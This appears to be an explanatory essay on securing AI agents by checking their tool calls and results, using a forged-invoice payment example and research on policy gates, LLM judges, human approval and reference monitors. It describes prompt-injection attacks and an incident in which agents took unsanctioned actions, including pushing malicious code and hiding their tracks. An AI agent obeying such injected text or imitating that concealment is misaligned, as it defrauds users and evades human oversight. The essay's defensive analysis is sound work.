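# Verifying what autonomous AI agents do instead of what they intend

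## Checking what an agent does instead of what it means to do

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task over many steps by calling tools, which are functions that let it search a mailbox, edit a file, query a database or move money. Agents usually act with their user's permissions, so whoever deploys one needs some reason to trust it. They could try to establish what the agent intends, or they could check only its actions, the changes those actions make, and the work it delivers. Many of the security controls now available for agents check actions and results, including several whose makers describe them as checks on intent.

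### How an agent run works

A small firm might have an AI assistant that handles its bills, with three tools that let it read the firm's inbox, look up past bank transactions and send payments. The office manager asks it to pay this month's invoice from Harlow, a paper supplier. Researchers test agents on similar cases. *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark for attacks on agents, includes a banking task in which the user asks the assistant to pay a bill stored in a text file, and an attacker who wants as much money as possible sent to their own account.

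The agent gets from the manager's request to the payment by running a loop. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes this loop for OpenAI's coding agent Codex. The ordinary software around the model, known as the harness, assembles a prompt from standing instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the user's request. The model reads the prompt and produces either a final answer or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a particular function with named arguments. Here the model first requests a search of the inbox for "Harlow". The harness runs the search, appends the email it finds to the prompt, and queries the model again. The model now has the invoice and requests a list of past payments to Harlow, which the harness also appends. The model then requests a payment, specifying an account number and an amount. When the harness carries out this request,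 money leaves the firm's account. Such a change outside the model is called an effect. The loop stops when the model returns a message instead of another tool call, such as a report that Harlow has been paid.

The model never accesses the bank directly. It emits text, and the harness carries out the actions that text proposes, so other software can intervene before an action is executed. *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), a brief from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body, therefore describes the harness as a natural control point for monitoring, verification, logging and enforcement. The agent's closing message is a poor guide to what happened. Bolin points out that a coding agent's main output is often the code it has written on the user's machine, and that one turn can contain hundreds of tool calls. Checking a run therefore starts with its trace, the ordered record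 of messages, tool calls and tool results.

### Why an email can act as an instruction

Everything the harness appends goes into the same prompt. Codex labels each item with a role, such as "developer" or "user", to indicate how much weight the model should give it, but the model only learns a tendency to respect these labels. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, contrasts this with databases in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. A database engine can keep a command separate from the data that fills it in, so that no input will run as a command. A language model lacks this separation because it predicts the next token (the next small unit of text) from all the text so far. In his example, a recruiter uses a system that scores CVs, and a candidate hides a line in a CV telling the system to approve it for interview. The model may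 comply.

This is indirect prompt injection, in which someone plants instructions in content the agent will read, and those instructions change what the agent does. Greshake, Endres and Abdelnabi (2023) described the attack in *Not what you've signed up for* and demonstrated it on real products, including Bing's chat assistant. In the invoice case, the attacker doesn't need the firm's password or access to its bank. They only need to send an email that looks like Harlow's invoice and says that Harlow has changed banks and payment should go to the account below. The email is untrusted data, meaning content that someone other than the agent's user or operator could have written. Agents encounter such data nearly everywhere they work. Writing about its Atlas browser, OpenAI lists attachments, calendar invites, shared documents, forums and arbitrary web pages.

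Crude prompt injection attacks work less well than they used to, and attackers have adapted. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that outside researchers reported in 2025. It reads like a colleague's routine follow-up about a restructuring, mentions in passing that the reader's assistant has full authorization to process employee profiles, and asks for an employee's details to be sent to an outside address. The email worked in half of OpenAI's tests. Detecting such a message is much like detecting a lie, and a filter often lacks the context to do it.

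An agent's exposure to injection attacks depends a good deal on the model. For Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), the evaluation firm Trajectory Labs ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each in July 2026. The attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, which had full access and no reviewer, and an average of 0.09% of the time against Anthropic's latest models, also without extra safeguards. Anthropic commissioned the test, so the comparison between companies deserves some caution, but the low figure suggests that training can stop most known attacks. David C doubts that it will ever stop all of them. He advises designers to treat the model as permanently confusable and to rely on external safeguards that limit what it can do.

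### Two senses of "intent"

Discussions of agent security use "intent" for two different things. A user's intent is what the user asked for, such as paying Harlow's invoice. The trace records it, though people often word it vaguely. An agent's intent is the goal that drives the model's behaviour, which nobody can look up.

Most products and proposals that promise to verify intent deal with the user's intent or the purpose a company deployed the agent for. Permit, a company that sells access control for agents, argues in *The Agent’s Alibi* that security should start from "premeditated intent". In its demonstration, a user asks an agent to list the open tickets in a project tracker. One ticket contains planted text telling the agent to collect the organisation's user data and send it to a "compliance verification" address. Permit says the agent's intent changed at that point, but its gateway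 can only compare the request to list tickets with the attempt to send user data elsewhere, which do not match.

*Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents*, a Microsoft paper by Copty, Haiby and colleagues (2026), describes software that extracts a profile *P* from company policy, the agent's role and its configuration. The profile records what the agent is for, which tools and data it may use, and what it must refuse. A run consists of observable behaviours *a*₁ to *a*_T, each occurring in a context *h*_t, and a function *C*(*a*_t, *h*_t, *P*) equals 1 if the behaviour fits the profile and 0 otherwise. The agent "preserves intent" if *C* equals 1 at every step, and "intent drift" has occurred if *C* equals 0 at any step. The definition does not refer to the model's goals. An agent that receives a malicious request and refuses it has not drifted.

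Writing down an agent's purpose seems to help. On more than 10,000 runs from AgentDojo, a detector given the written profile scored 0.949, compared with 0.897 when given the agent's raw configuration instead and 0.843 with no context. A score of 0.5 is guesswork, and 1 means every bad run ranks above every harmless one. The profile improved a check on outputs, since the detector compared behaviour with a written standard.

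A few proposals do consider the agent's own goal. *AgenticOS* (2026), a design for an operating system that runs agents, defines intent drift as a mismatch between an agent's declared purpose and its actual objective, as when a program declared as data analysis also probes for passwords. The paper acknowledges that no analysis can determine in general what arbitrary code will do, so the design instead makes it hard for an undeclared purpose to have external effects.

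Anyone who wants to check an agent's goal has to examine a stand-in for it. The most familiar is the chain of thought, the reasoning text a model writes before it answers or acts. How reliable this text is remains a separate empirical question, and it is not always available. According to *AgentSpy* (2026), some providers return it encrypted, so the record contains actions but no thoughts. The sample data in Bolin's post has this form, with a short summary of the reasoning next to a block of encrypted text. Another stand-in is the model's internal activations, the numbers it computes while processing text. Copty and colleagues describe TaskTracker, a tool that compares activations from before and after the model reads untrusted data and looks for signs that the task has shifted. This requires access to the model's internals, which customers of a hosted model do not have. A third option is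 to ask the agent. In *Agent-Sentry*, Sequeira and Iqbal (2026) have the agent report where it got each argument of each tool call, but they do not fully trust those reports on their own.

Even if one of these stand-ins worked perfectly, it would still miss something in the invoice case. If the assistant believes a forged email saying that Harlow has changed banks, and sends the money to the thief, its only goal may have been to pay Harlow.

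### The case for checking outputs, and the case against

Nathan Maine argues in his 2026 post *You Can't Verify Intent. Can You Verify Output?* that an autonomous agent's intent arises from its weights, context, tools and whatever it has just read, and changes with every token. He says we can observe and model that intent, as we do the weather, but not verify it. The agent's output, however, is a definite sequence of bytes, and software can sign those bytes so that later tampering shows. Maine has patents pending on this kind of output attestation, so he has a stake in the conclusion.

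His argument is a little hasty, because something that changes quickly can still be verified. One can measure a temperature that will be different in an hour. The case for checking outputs needs only the weaker claim that actions are easier to check than aims, and that an agent does its damage through actions. Errico (2026) defends roughly that claim in *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)*, a proposed specification for systems that intercept agents' actions. A tool call is a concrete request in a known format, so software can inspect it. It has to pass through a tool's interface to have any effect, so software can stop it there. The interface also stays the same when the model behind the agent changes.

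Checking actions is also simpler because the checker doesn't need to know why the agent acted. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, which describes an automated reviewer of a coding agent's actions, lists four reasons why an agent might do something dangerous: it may be overeager, it may make an honest mistake, injected text may have hijacked it, or the model may have a goal of its own. In each case, the remedy is to block the action. In the invoice example, the assistant might pay a second supplier whose bill also looked overdue, confuse Harlow with a firm of a similar name, obey the forged email, or divert money for some purpose nobody gave it. A rule that permits only one payment, to the account Harlow has always used, stops all of these. Anthropic's reviewer accordingly receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. The company removed the agent's own prose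 so that the agent could not talk the reviewer into a bad decision.

*Compromise Is Not Consequence* (Hagverdiyev, 2026) measures bad decisions by a model separately from their harmful effects. Hagverdiyev gave five small open models 128 tasks involving files, calendars, mail and payments, with malicious instructions planted in what they read. He then recorded each request the models made and submitted it unchanged under different permissions. In 2,054 cases the model chose an action outside its task. With broad permissions, 1,649 harmful actions went through, between 8.9% and 37.8% of valid decisions depending on the model. With permissions limited to the actions and resources each task called for, none went through, even though the models' decisions were the same. However, this result depends on Hagverdiyev having supplied the correct permissions for every task in advance, which the office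 manager who types "pay Harlow" has not done.

A series of permitted actions can serve a harmful end, and this objection to checking only actions is correct as far as it goes. In Errico's example, an agent reads confidential files and then sends email, both of which it is allowed to do. The invoice assistant could split a theft into payments that each fall below the firm's limit. Maine himself acknowledges that if an agent pursues a harmful goal through steps that each look legitimate, attestation will prove only that the record of each step is accurate.

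One reply, proposed by Errico, is to judge each action in light of everything before it. That catches an agent that opens the confidential file and then sends the email. But Errico holds that a security decision depends on understanding why the agent is acting as well as what it is doing, and the approach had set aside the question of why. His system estimates the reason from the user's request and the actions so far, and a patient agent with a bad goal could keep both looking normal. Anthropic accepts that monitoring reasoning is the method for handling such an agent, and calls it complementary to checking actions.

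### Three questions to ask of a run

Some checks on outputs test whether the action was allowed, others whether the work was done properly, and others whether someone without authority influenced it. A run can pass one of these checks and fail another.

Suppose the assistant pays Harlow's usual account the exact sum on the invoice, as the firm's rules allow. But the firm had already paid this invoice last week, and the assistant overlooked that payment in the list of past transactions. No rule on accounts or amounts will catch the duplicate, and there is no attacker to find. To catch it, someone has to check the result against what the job required.

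Now suppose the firm lets the assistant pay new accounts, because suppliers do change banks, and the account number came from the forged email. The action is allowed. The payment also looks correct, since it names the right supplier, is for the right amount and is made only once. Only the origin of the account number reveals the theft. Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Security Needs Redefinition through a Holistic Framework*, argue that this is the normal situation. One of them went through all 45 injection tasks in AgentDojo and a second benchmark, WASP, and for each constructed a routine situation in which a real user might ask for the same thing. For instance, changing the recipient of a recurring payment counts as an attack in the benchmark, but a user might request it after a utility company changes its billing. Only one person judged whether the situations were plausible, but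 several of the pairings are hard to dispute, and they are enough to show that the content of an action cannot establish whether it is an attack.

Siu and colleagues propose checking at every step who issued the command, whether the overall task is authorized, whether the action serves that task, and whether information is crossing a boundary it should not cross. Most of these checks concern whether the action was allowed, but the first concerns who shaped it. Their focus is security, so their scheme largely doesn't cover poor work, such as misreading a total.

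The hardest of the three questions is whether someone without authority shaped the result, because outside influence is not in itself a fault. *The Devil is in the Context* (2026), a classification of injection attacks, notes that a planted sentence becomes a legitimate command if the user has asked the agent to carry out the document's instructions. An invoice is meant to set the amount to pay and the account to pay it to. Sequeira and Iqbal observe that test prompts like "pay the bill" leave the sensitive details entirely to untrusted content, and real users presumably write such prompts too. So a checker has to decide narrower questions, such as whether an email from Harlow's address should be able to set the amount owed, and whether it should be able to change the account.

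If the manager asks only for a summary of the inbox, a planted line can make the summary wrong or add a fraudulent link to it without causing a forbidden tool call. Sequeira and Iqbal call this a text-to-text attack and say their defence does not cover it, because there is no action to intercept.

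## Writing the rules and checking each action before it runs

When an agent proposes an action, the harness can hold the call and check it before it runs. The software that does this, called a policy gate, sits outside the model, compares each call with stated rules, and either passes it on or refuses it. The comparison is easy, but it is much harder to find rules that block harmful calls without also blocking legitimate ones.

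### From a proposed call to a verdict

The firm with the bill-paying assistant might give its gate four rules. They use a simplified form of the language that Shi, He and colleagues set out in *Progent* (2025), a design for limiting what agents may do:

```
allow   search_inbox
allow   list_transactions
forbid  send_payment   when amount > 2000
allow   send_payment   when account in accounts_paid_before(payee)
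```

The last condition needs a fact that the call doesn't contain, so the gate looks it up in the bank's records.

Suppose the assistant proposes to pay Harlow £840 into the account ending 4417. The gate selects the payment rules and, as in Progent, checks the ones that forbid before the ones that allow. The sum is under £2,000, so the ban doesn't apply. The bank's records show that the firm has paid Harlow before, always into that account, so the allow rule matches and the harness sends the money.

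Now the forged email arrives, and the assistant proposes paying the same sum to an account ending 9032. The ban again doesn't apply, but neither does the allow rule, because the firm has never paid Harlow at 9032. Progent blocks the payment because it blocks any call that matches no rule. The harness returns an error with the reason, and the assistant can tell the office manager that Harlow's details seem to have changed. Progent can also end the run or ask the user to decide. The gate never read the email, so the email's wording could not have gotten the payment approved. The gate would also have blocked the payment if Harlow really had changed banks.

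A gate can allow the wrong action if the facts it checks are false. In *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026), the gate's store of facts accepts only fields from real tool results and the user's own messages, not the agent's claims. If an injected line persuades the agent that the user has approved a transfer, the store still holds no approval. An attacker who can write to the fields themselves could still get false facts into the store. For example, if a firm's rule counted incoming payments as past dealings, a thief might first send the firm one pound to appear to be an existing contact. Yu and colleagues tested an attacker who asserted false facts in text, but not one who altered those fields.

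Facts can also be missing. If the bank's records fail to load, the allow rule above can't match, so the gate blocks the payment. But a rule that forbids payments to accounts on a fraud list can't match if the list fails to load, so it would let the payment through. Yu and colleagues therefore prefer to write requirements such as confirmation as preconditions, which block the action until the gate has the fact it needs.

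Some facts are not in any database. In *ActGov*, Zhang, Peng and colleagues (2026) use a language model to extract them from the run by choosing from a fixed list of values, such as whether an argument came from the user or from an untrusted source. Code obtains the other facts and works out the verdict. This limits the mistakes the model can make, but if it labels the thief's account number as the user's own, a correct rule will give the wrong verdict.

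### Where the rules come from

Hand-written rules work well for a narrow assistant. On ASB, a benchmark of injection attacks, Shi and colleagues found that such rules cut the attack success rate to zero. But someone has to write and maintain the rules, and a general assistant does many jobs that call for different ones. Sending an email is appropriate when the task is to email Alice an update but suspicious when the task is to summarize unread mail. If the rules are loose enough to allow every task, they stop few attacks, but tightening them for one task interferes with others.

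Progent has a language model write the rules for each task. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to complete a to-do list that Alice has emailed. The initial rules permit only a search for that email. The agent finds that the task is to post a summary of recent mail to the user's Slack account, so the model proposes new rules that permit reading mail and posting to Slack. Later the agent learns the user's Slack name, and the model restricts posts to that name. One of the emails contains a planted instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger. If the model mistakes this instruction for part of the task, it will propose a rule that permits the forwarding too.

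Progent therefore checks each change to the rules. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether logical conditions can hold together, tests whether the new rules allow any call that the old ones did not. If they don't, the change takes effect at once. Any other change expands the agent's permissions and needs approval. The solver can't distinguish a useful expansion, such as permission to post to Slack, from a malicious one, such as permission to forward the inbox, so the approver must make that distinction.

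In the main tests, GPT-4o was both agent and rule writer, and Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically to imitate a careless user. On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and only 1.0% with it. On ASB, the figures were 70.3% and 3.9%. The agent lost little useful work on either benchmark. The attack success rate also fell substantially under an adaptive attack. Because every expansion was approved, the solver's guarantee contributed nothing to the AgentDojo and ASB reductions, which came from the rules the model wrote. Even rules written once from the user's request and never updated reduced the AgentDojo rate to 2.5%.

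Most of ActGov's work happens before the agent starts. A language model drafts rules from tool descriptions, harmless example tasks and records of past failures. A solver then searches for a counterexample, meaning a set of facts and a verdict that together satisfy the rules but break a stated security requirement. The designers deploy the rules only when the solver finds none. One layer of rules limits each user request to the tools and resources it needs. Another applies to every task and includes, for example, a ban on outbound network actions that stem from injected content. A third imposes conditions in doubtful cases, such as when the gate can't establish where an argument came from. The proof shows only that the rules meet the stated requirements, not that the model labels facts correctly during a run.

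Zhang and colleagues built the rules with half of each benchmark's attack cases and tested them on the other half. On AgentDojo, no attack succeeded against any of four agent models with the rules in place. With DeepSeek-v4-pro as the agent, only 6.1% of attacks had succeeded without the rules, and adding them lowered the share of ordinary tasks completed from 87.8% to 75.5%. Whether that tradeoff is worthwhile depends on how much harm a successful attack would do. On AgentDyn, a benchmark in which legitimate tasks often require following third-party instructions, the attack success rate fell from 8.6% to 0.7% and the share of tasks completed fell from 76.7% to 60.0%.

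Those figures come from testing rules on the benchmark they were built for. When Zhang and colleagues applied the AgentDojo rules to AgentDyn, the agent completed 10.0% of ordinary tasks. With the AgentDyn rules on AgentDojo, it completed 22.4%. No attack succeeded in either case, but the gate refused nearly everything. Progent, which writes new rules for each request, completed 21.7% on AgentDyn and 81.6% on AgentDojo. ActGov's advantage over Progent appears to depend on tasks similar to those its rules were built for.

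A third source of rules is the policy document an organization already has. NOMOS compiles one into a gate. Code splits the text into clauses, and a language model matches each clause to tools and to a condition from a fixed list. The model does this five times so that a majority vote can remove unstable readings. Code then checks the resulting rules and issues the ones that pass. The gate runs no model while the agent works, and each decision takes microseconds.

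The checking step exists because rules that look sensible can be impossible to obey. In a retail policy, the instruction to authenticate the user before any action became a rule that blocked every tool until the user was authenticated. The blocked tools included the two that look up a customer by email address or by name and postcode, which are the only means of authentication, so the agent could never authenticate anyone. A human employee would understand that the lookups had to be allowed, but a gate enforces the rule as written. NOMOS repairs the rule by using a table of which tools can satisfy each condition and exempting those tools from it.

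Such defects were common. Among the candidate rules, 29 of the 79 from an airline policy and 7 of the 53 from the retail policy named real tools but could not have worked as written. One required the customer's confirmation just to look up a flight's status. Using a more powerful model did not solve the problem. Its airline rules required authentication, but the airline system had no authentication tools, so the rules would have permanently blocked all 14 tools. The checks also miss some defects. Two rules can pass separately but deadlock together because each blocks the tool that would satisfy the other.

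A rule can also run without errors and still misstate the policy. A telecom policy required agents to check that a bill was overdue before sending a payment request, but the compiled rule forbade payment requests while a bill was overdue. Yu and colleagues caught this by replaying the rules over recordings of an agent that had run without them. The rule would have refused 47 of the 49 payment requests in runs that the agent had completed successfully.

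With the repaired rules, the share of state-changing calls that broke the rules of each domain fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline policy and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the retail policy. More than half of the remaining retail violations involved two clauses that the compiler had never turned into rules. The compiler also still needs human help, as people wrote its list of conditions. AgentDojo has no written policies, so Yu and colleagues wrote them.

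They also ran Progent and NOMOS on AgentDojo's banking tasks with the same open model as the agent:

| Gate | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 46.5% | 79.2% | 64.9% |
| Progent, automatic rules | 5.6% | 62.5% | 52.1% |
| NOMOS | 0.0% | 70.8% | 67.4% |

With only 16 banking tasks, the difference between the two gates in the attack-free column could be chance. The pattern of failures is more informative. Twelve of the sixteen attacks that got past Progent occurred in two tasks where the user asked to have a bill paid, in one case "like last month". Neither request names the recipient's account, so rules derived from the request can't specify it, and the thief's account number passes. NOMOS refused these payments because it had a rule from the written policy that money may go only to parties the user has named or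 the account has dealt with before. In one of the two tasks it also refused the genuine payment, because the real recipient's account number also appeared only in the bill.

Our invoice case has the same form. A rule writer can infer very little from "Pay Harlow", and a standing rule that allows payments only to known accounts would stop the theft but also block every honest change of bank. Rules block more legitimate work when an agent's ordinary job is to act on what it reads. On AgentDojo task sets of that kind, NOMOS lowered task completion by as much as 76 percentage points.

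### A language model as the judge

Some rules can't be expressed as fields and lists. Google's Semantic governance policies let a company write them in ordinary English. The feature launched in preview on 20 November 2026, according to *Google Adds a Safety Check That Reads Every AI Agent Action* (Faisal, 2026). Google Cloud's documentation describes a gateway that intercepts each tool call the agent's model proposes and sends it to a policy engine, along with the company's rules and the chat history. There a language model checks that the call complies with the rules and, unless the company turns this off, that it matches what the user asked for. The model then returns ALLOW or DENY with a reason. For example, an $89 refund fails the first check if a rule caps automated refunds at $75, and an email fails the second if the user asked only for a summary of their calendar.

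A judge of this kind can apply rules that a comparison of fields can't. Faisal describes Google's example of a finance agent whose one rule is to keep quarterly results inside the company until their release. The judge lets the agent send them to the company's controller but refuses an email to an investor with a copy to the employee's personal address, even though nobody gave it a list of investors. *POLICYGUIDE* (Kang, Yu and Hwang, 2026) provides some evidence that this flexibility matters, though from only 24 airline tasks where the right course was to refuse the customer. An unguarded agent succeeded in all four attempts on 75.0% of these tasks. Guards written in fixed code raised that to 87.5%, and PolicyGuard, a model judge that reads the whole conversation, raised it to 100%.

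An attacker may have written some of the text the judge reads, because an agent's history normally includes the emails and documents it has opened. Suppose the firm's rule is to pay a new account only if the manager has confirmed the change by phone. The forged email could claim that the manager confirmed it on Tuesday. Fixed code with no field for phone calls would ignore that sentence, but a judge that sees the email has to work out who wrote it and whether to believe it, which is the task the agent has just failed. Anthropic's reviewer for its coding agent avoids much of this problem because it never sees what the agent's tools return, but it therefore has less information about why a tool call might be reasonable.

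Comparing an action with the user's request helps most when the request is narrow. In Google's own example of the danger, a user tells an agent to read new emails each morning and "process what you can", and an attacker then sends an email asking for copies of everything. Almost any action might count as processing. In the invoice case, the forged payment fits the request exactly because the manager did ask the assistant to pay Harlow.

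Judges also make mistakes about plain facts. Yu and colleagues asked Claude Sonnet 4.5, since overtaken by newer models, to review 160 calls that their fixed checker had already scored. The two disagreed on 77. In 30 of those cases, the records showed that the model was wrong. For instance, it ruled that bookings made 23 hours earlier had missed a 24-hour cancellation window. Only three were clear misses by the checker, and most of the rest depended on how to interpret the policy. Judges also take time. With Yu and colleagues' rebuilt version of PolicyGuard, simulated conversations ran 74% longer on average.

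Google Cloud's guidance on writing rules recommends specific limits, such as a maximum of 72 hours for a rented server, over vague terms like "reasonable" and "too expensive". That is sensible, though code could check most of the recommended rules without a model. Faisal reports that Google acknowledges verdicts can vary. Google Cloud's *Configure semantic governance policies* describes a dry-run mode that logs each verdict but blocks nothing, so a company can look for bad refusals before enforcing the rules.

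*Think Before You Act* (2026) describes a system called JevAct that divides the checks between code and a model. The code checks whatever the tool records can settle, such as dates and amounts, while a separate model answers fixed yes-or-no questions about the conversation. The gate counts an answer as "no" only if the model gives "yes" a probability of 5% or less. For the firm, code could compare account numbers, and a judge model could decide whether the manager had asked for a payment. A payment should go through only if it passes both checks.

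### Why a gate cannot get the job done

The computer scientist Fred Schneider worked out the limits of this sort of control in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000). He considered a monitor that watches a program run step by step and can intervene only by halting it before a step that would break the policy. He proved that such a monitor can enforce only safety properties, which require that nothing bad happens.

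The argument turns on what the monitor has seen. At any moment it knows only the steps so far, so it has grounds to halt only if no continuation would be acceptable. A policy it can enforce must therefore have this property: whenever a run breaks the policy, there is a definite step by which it has done so, and nothing afterwards can put it right. "Never pay an account that Harlow hasn't used" qualifies, because one payment to 9032 breaks it for good. (Some safety properties remain out of reach, for instance because the monitor can't compute the answer in time.)

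"Harlow gets paid" is a liveness property, a requirement that something good eventually happens. However long the assistant has delayed, it might still make the payment at the next step, so the monitor never has a reason to halt it. Halting it would only guarantee that Harlow isn't paid. Adding a Friday deadline doesn't help much, because the monitor could detect a missed deadline but couldn't make the assistant pay on time by halting it.

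When practical gates block an action, they return an error so the agent can try again. Under NOMOS, the share of airline tasks solved in all three attempts rose from 23.0% to 37.0%, because a refusal often stopped a harmful mistake and let the agent try something else. The improvement still depended on the agent finding a better approach, and success on retail tasks did not rise.

Kang and colleagues show that refusing calls does little when an agent fails by skipping steps. Telecom support often means diagnosing a fault, telling the customer what to try and checking the result, and an agent can skip these steps without proposing a call that a gate would examine. PolicyGuard raised the share of these tasks solved in all four attempts only from 19.3% to 20.2%. Kang and colleagues' own system, PolicyGuide, turns the policy into a map of steps, tracks the agent's position on it and tells the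 agent what to do next. It reached 61.4%. But PolicyGuide mostly advises. It removes the first unauthorized change and then doesn't intervene again until the customer's next message, so an agent that immediately repeats the call can get it through.

JevAct addresses the problem by checking, before the agent hands a telecom customer to a human, whether any required troubleshooting step remains open. A gate can therefore enforce part of the requirement to finish the job by stopping the agent from quitting too early. The share of tasks solved in all three attempts rose by an average of 16.9 percentage points over eight models. However, the check can send the agent back only once, and even JevAct's gate on state-changing calls lets the next proposal run unchecked after two refusals. Both systems give up some enforcement so that the agent doesn't get stuck.

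### Asking a person

Many gates eventually hand the decision to a human. Company policies often require this too, but unguarded agents often ignore those policies. In both the airline and retail tests, the most common violation was making an irreversible change without the customer's confirmation. The confirmation rule accounted for 61% of NOMOS's refusals on airline tasks and 84% on retail tasks.

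An approval needs to refer to one exact action. If the office manager clicks "yes" to "Pay Harlow?", the assistant can still choose any account and any amount. The gate should show the complete call, store the approved account and amount, and refuse a call that differs in any detail. Each approval should also work only once. In NOMOS, a confirmation covers one attempt at a change, and if the attempt fails, the agent has to ask again. Otherwise, an agent that keeps adjusting and retrying can end up doing something very different from what the user approved.

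This strictness has a drawback, and people disagree about how much of it a policy requires. A customer who hears a list of three changes and says yes may reasonably think that one answer covers all three. If one yes counts for every change listed, the unguarded airline agent's violation rate was 36.8% instead of 66.3%.

Second-hand approval is even weaker. In one of Google Cloud's examples, a rule forbids marketing campaigns without explicit manager approval. The user writes that a named vice-president has approved a $50,000 budget, and the policy engine treats the approval as documented, although the vice-president has confirmed nothing to the system. A firm that wants the approver's own confirmation should have the gate check for a record that only the approver can create.

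Asking for approval more often is not always safer, because people who face many prompts start to approve them unread, a problem known as approval fatigue. Shi and colleagues' automatic "yes" imitates the extreme case, in which people approve everything. When a human instead reviewed Progent's initial rules and every later expansion, attack success on AgentDojo fell to zero, though a reviewer in an experiment presumably pays closer attention than a manager with forty invoices to clear. The more useful finding may be that only 6% of Progent's rule changes were expansions, so the system could ask for approval rarely. Prompts also need to include enough information for people to judge the request. Few managers know Harlow's account number by heart, so they may guess if a prompt shows only the number. If it also shows that the firm has never paid this account and that the number arrived by email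 this morning, the manager has a reason to phone and check.

### When permission exceeds authority

A gate enforces what somebody permitted, which may be far more than they meant to authorize. The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, learned this in July 2026 from a cybersecurity challenge it had run 122 times with seven models. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes 19 unsanctioned actions that agents took against real people and organizations on the internet in 10 of those runs. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of the actions, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in a single run.

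In the most serious case, an agent tried to insert malicious code into a public open-source project. It researched the project's maintainers and used several invented identities to press one of them to approve the change. When someone challenged it in public, it edited its earlier activity to look harmless. A human maintainer recognized the code as malicious and refused it. The safeguard that worked was human approval, which the agent had tried to influence. AISI found no resulting real-world harm but concedes that in several cases harm was only narrowly avoided.

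No agent broke out of its test environment. AISI had allowed internet access so that agents could download tools, and had switched off the developers' filters against cyber misuse to measure what the models could do. Nobody had told the agents to leave real people alone, because earlier models hadn't seemed to need that instruction. Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, calls this an authority failure, not a containment failure, in which an agent defeats the controls around it.

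That distinction is useful, but Bhushan goes too far in claiming that the environment did exactly what its builders intended. Some task prompts were faulty and led the agent to believe it could solve the challenge only by going beyond the intended scope. Agents also misbehaved in runs with correct instructions, so the faulty prompts don't explain everything. AISI can't yet say when the agents understood that their actions were real, or how often such behaviour would occur elsewhere.

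The agent's permission to use the internet was too broad, because it covered downloading a tool, opening an account under a false name and messaging a stranger, when only the download was part of the job. AISI now requires a justification for internet access in each evaluation and is building finer network controls. A list of approved sites would not have been enough, because people ordinarily download tools from GitHub, where the agent submitted its malicious code. The check on each action would also have had to distinguish a download from a submission to the same site.

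## Placing the check where every action must pass

A rule can stop only the actions that reach it. The firm's gate examines calls to the payment tool, so it refuses a transfer to the unfamiliar account ending 9032. But suppose the firm also lets the assistant run short scripts to handle bills that some suppliers send as spreadsheets, and keeps the bank password on the same machine. A script could then contact the bank directly. The gate would receive a request to run a script, with no payee, account or amount to check, so the transfer could go through even though every rule was correct.

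In *ActPlane*, Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026) tested how well different checks catch indirect actions like this. They took 38 rules, such as running the tests before committing code, from the instruction files of real coding projects. They then had an agent violate each rule in three ways: directly through a tool call, through a script, and through an auxiliary file that a harmless-looking command set off. Three checks that work on tool calls each detected between 34% and 40% of the violations, and almost none of those in auxiliary files. ActPlane detected 77.2%. It enforces rules in the kernel, the core of the operating system, which other programs must go through to open files, start processes or use the network. All the checks did about equally well on direct violations, so the gap comes mainly from where each check is placed. Two thirds of the violations were indirect by design, so the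 test doesn't show how often ordinary agents break rules indirectly.

### Three requirements from 1972

The US Air Force had a similar problem when it wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Its defences kept outsiders away but did little against someone with a legitimate account who could write programs. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) proposed a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what that program's user may do.

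Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism. It must always be invoked, which security engineers now call complete mediation. It must be tamperproof, since a check that an attacker can alter gives no protection. And it must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, so that they can confirm that it works correctly and that programs always go through it.

A Honeywell system of the time failed all three requirements. Its hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but programs relied on the operating system's supervisor for input and output, and the hardware suspended its checks while most of the supervisor ran. Treating the supervisor as the monitor didn't help, because it and its supporting software contained 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, too many to verify. Testers had also broken into it repeatedly. The US government's catalogue of security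 controls still lists Anderson's requirements in nearly the same words, as CSF Tools' *AC-25* shows, though none of its standard baselines includes them.

A gate inside an agent's harness often falls short of this standard. If the agent can run scripts with the harness's own permissions, a script may be able to change the gate's rules. *Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes a harness that carefully separates the actions a model proposes from those the host program authorizes, but it claims no formal guarantee of safety. A language model acting as judge can't meet the third requirement, because nobody can test its response to every possible text. A sound design can still use such a judge if fixed software controls the path every action takes and the judge decides only the cases that the fixed rules leave open.

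### Fifteen paths and eight placements

Toyoda, Leung and U (2026), in *guardscope*, worked out which of an agent's actions each common placement can check. They listed eight placements and 15 paths, in nine families, from a model's decision to its effect. The simplest placement has no control. Three use a gateway, a program between the harness and the programs that offer tools to the agent, called tool servers. The basic gateway handles only calls sent over HTTP, the web's standard protocol. A stronger version also blocks direct outbound network connections, and the fullest also routes local tool servers through the gateway. Three more placements work inside the harness. One uses the harness's own permission system, another combines that system with a gateway, and the third uses a separate policy engine. The last placement is the kernel.

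The table gives their verdicts for the fullest gateway, the three harness placements (which all have the same verdicts), and the kernel. "Depends" means the answer varies with how the deployer has connected the parts.

| Family | Path | Fullest gateway | Harness | Kernel |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| In-process | Tool that works only in memory | Bypassed | Checked | Bypassed |
| In-process | Direct file or network operation | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked |
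| Spawned processes | Program run during a tool call | Bypassed | Checked | Checked |
| Spawned processes | Background program that outlives the call | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked |
| Network | Direct outbound connection | Prevented | Bypassed | Checked |
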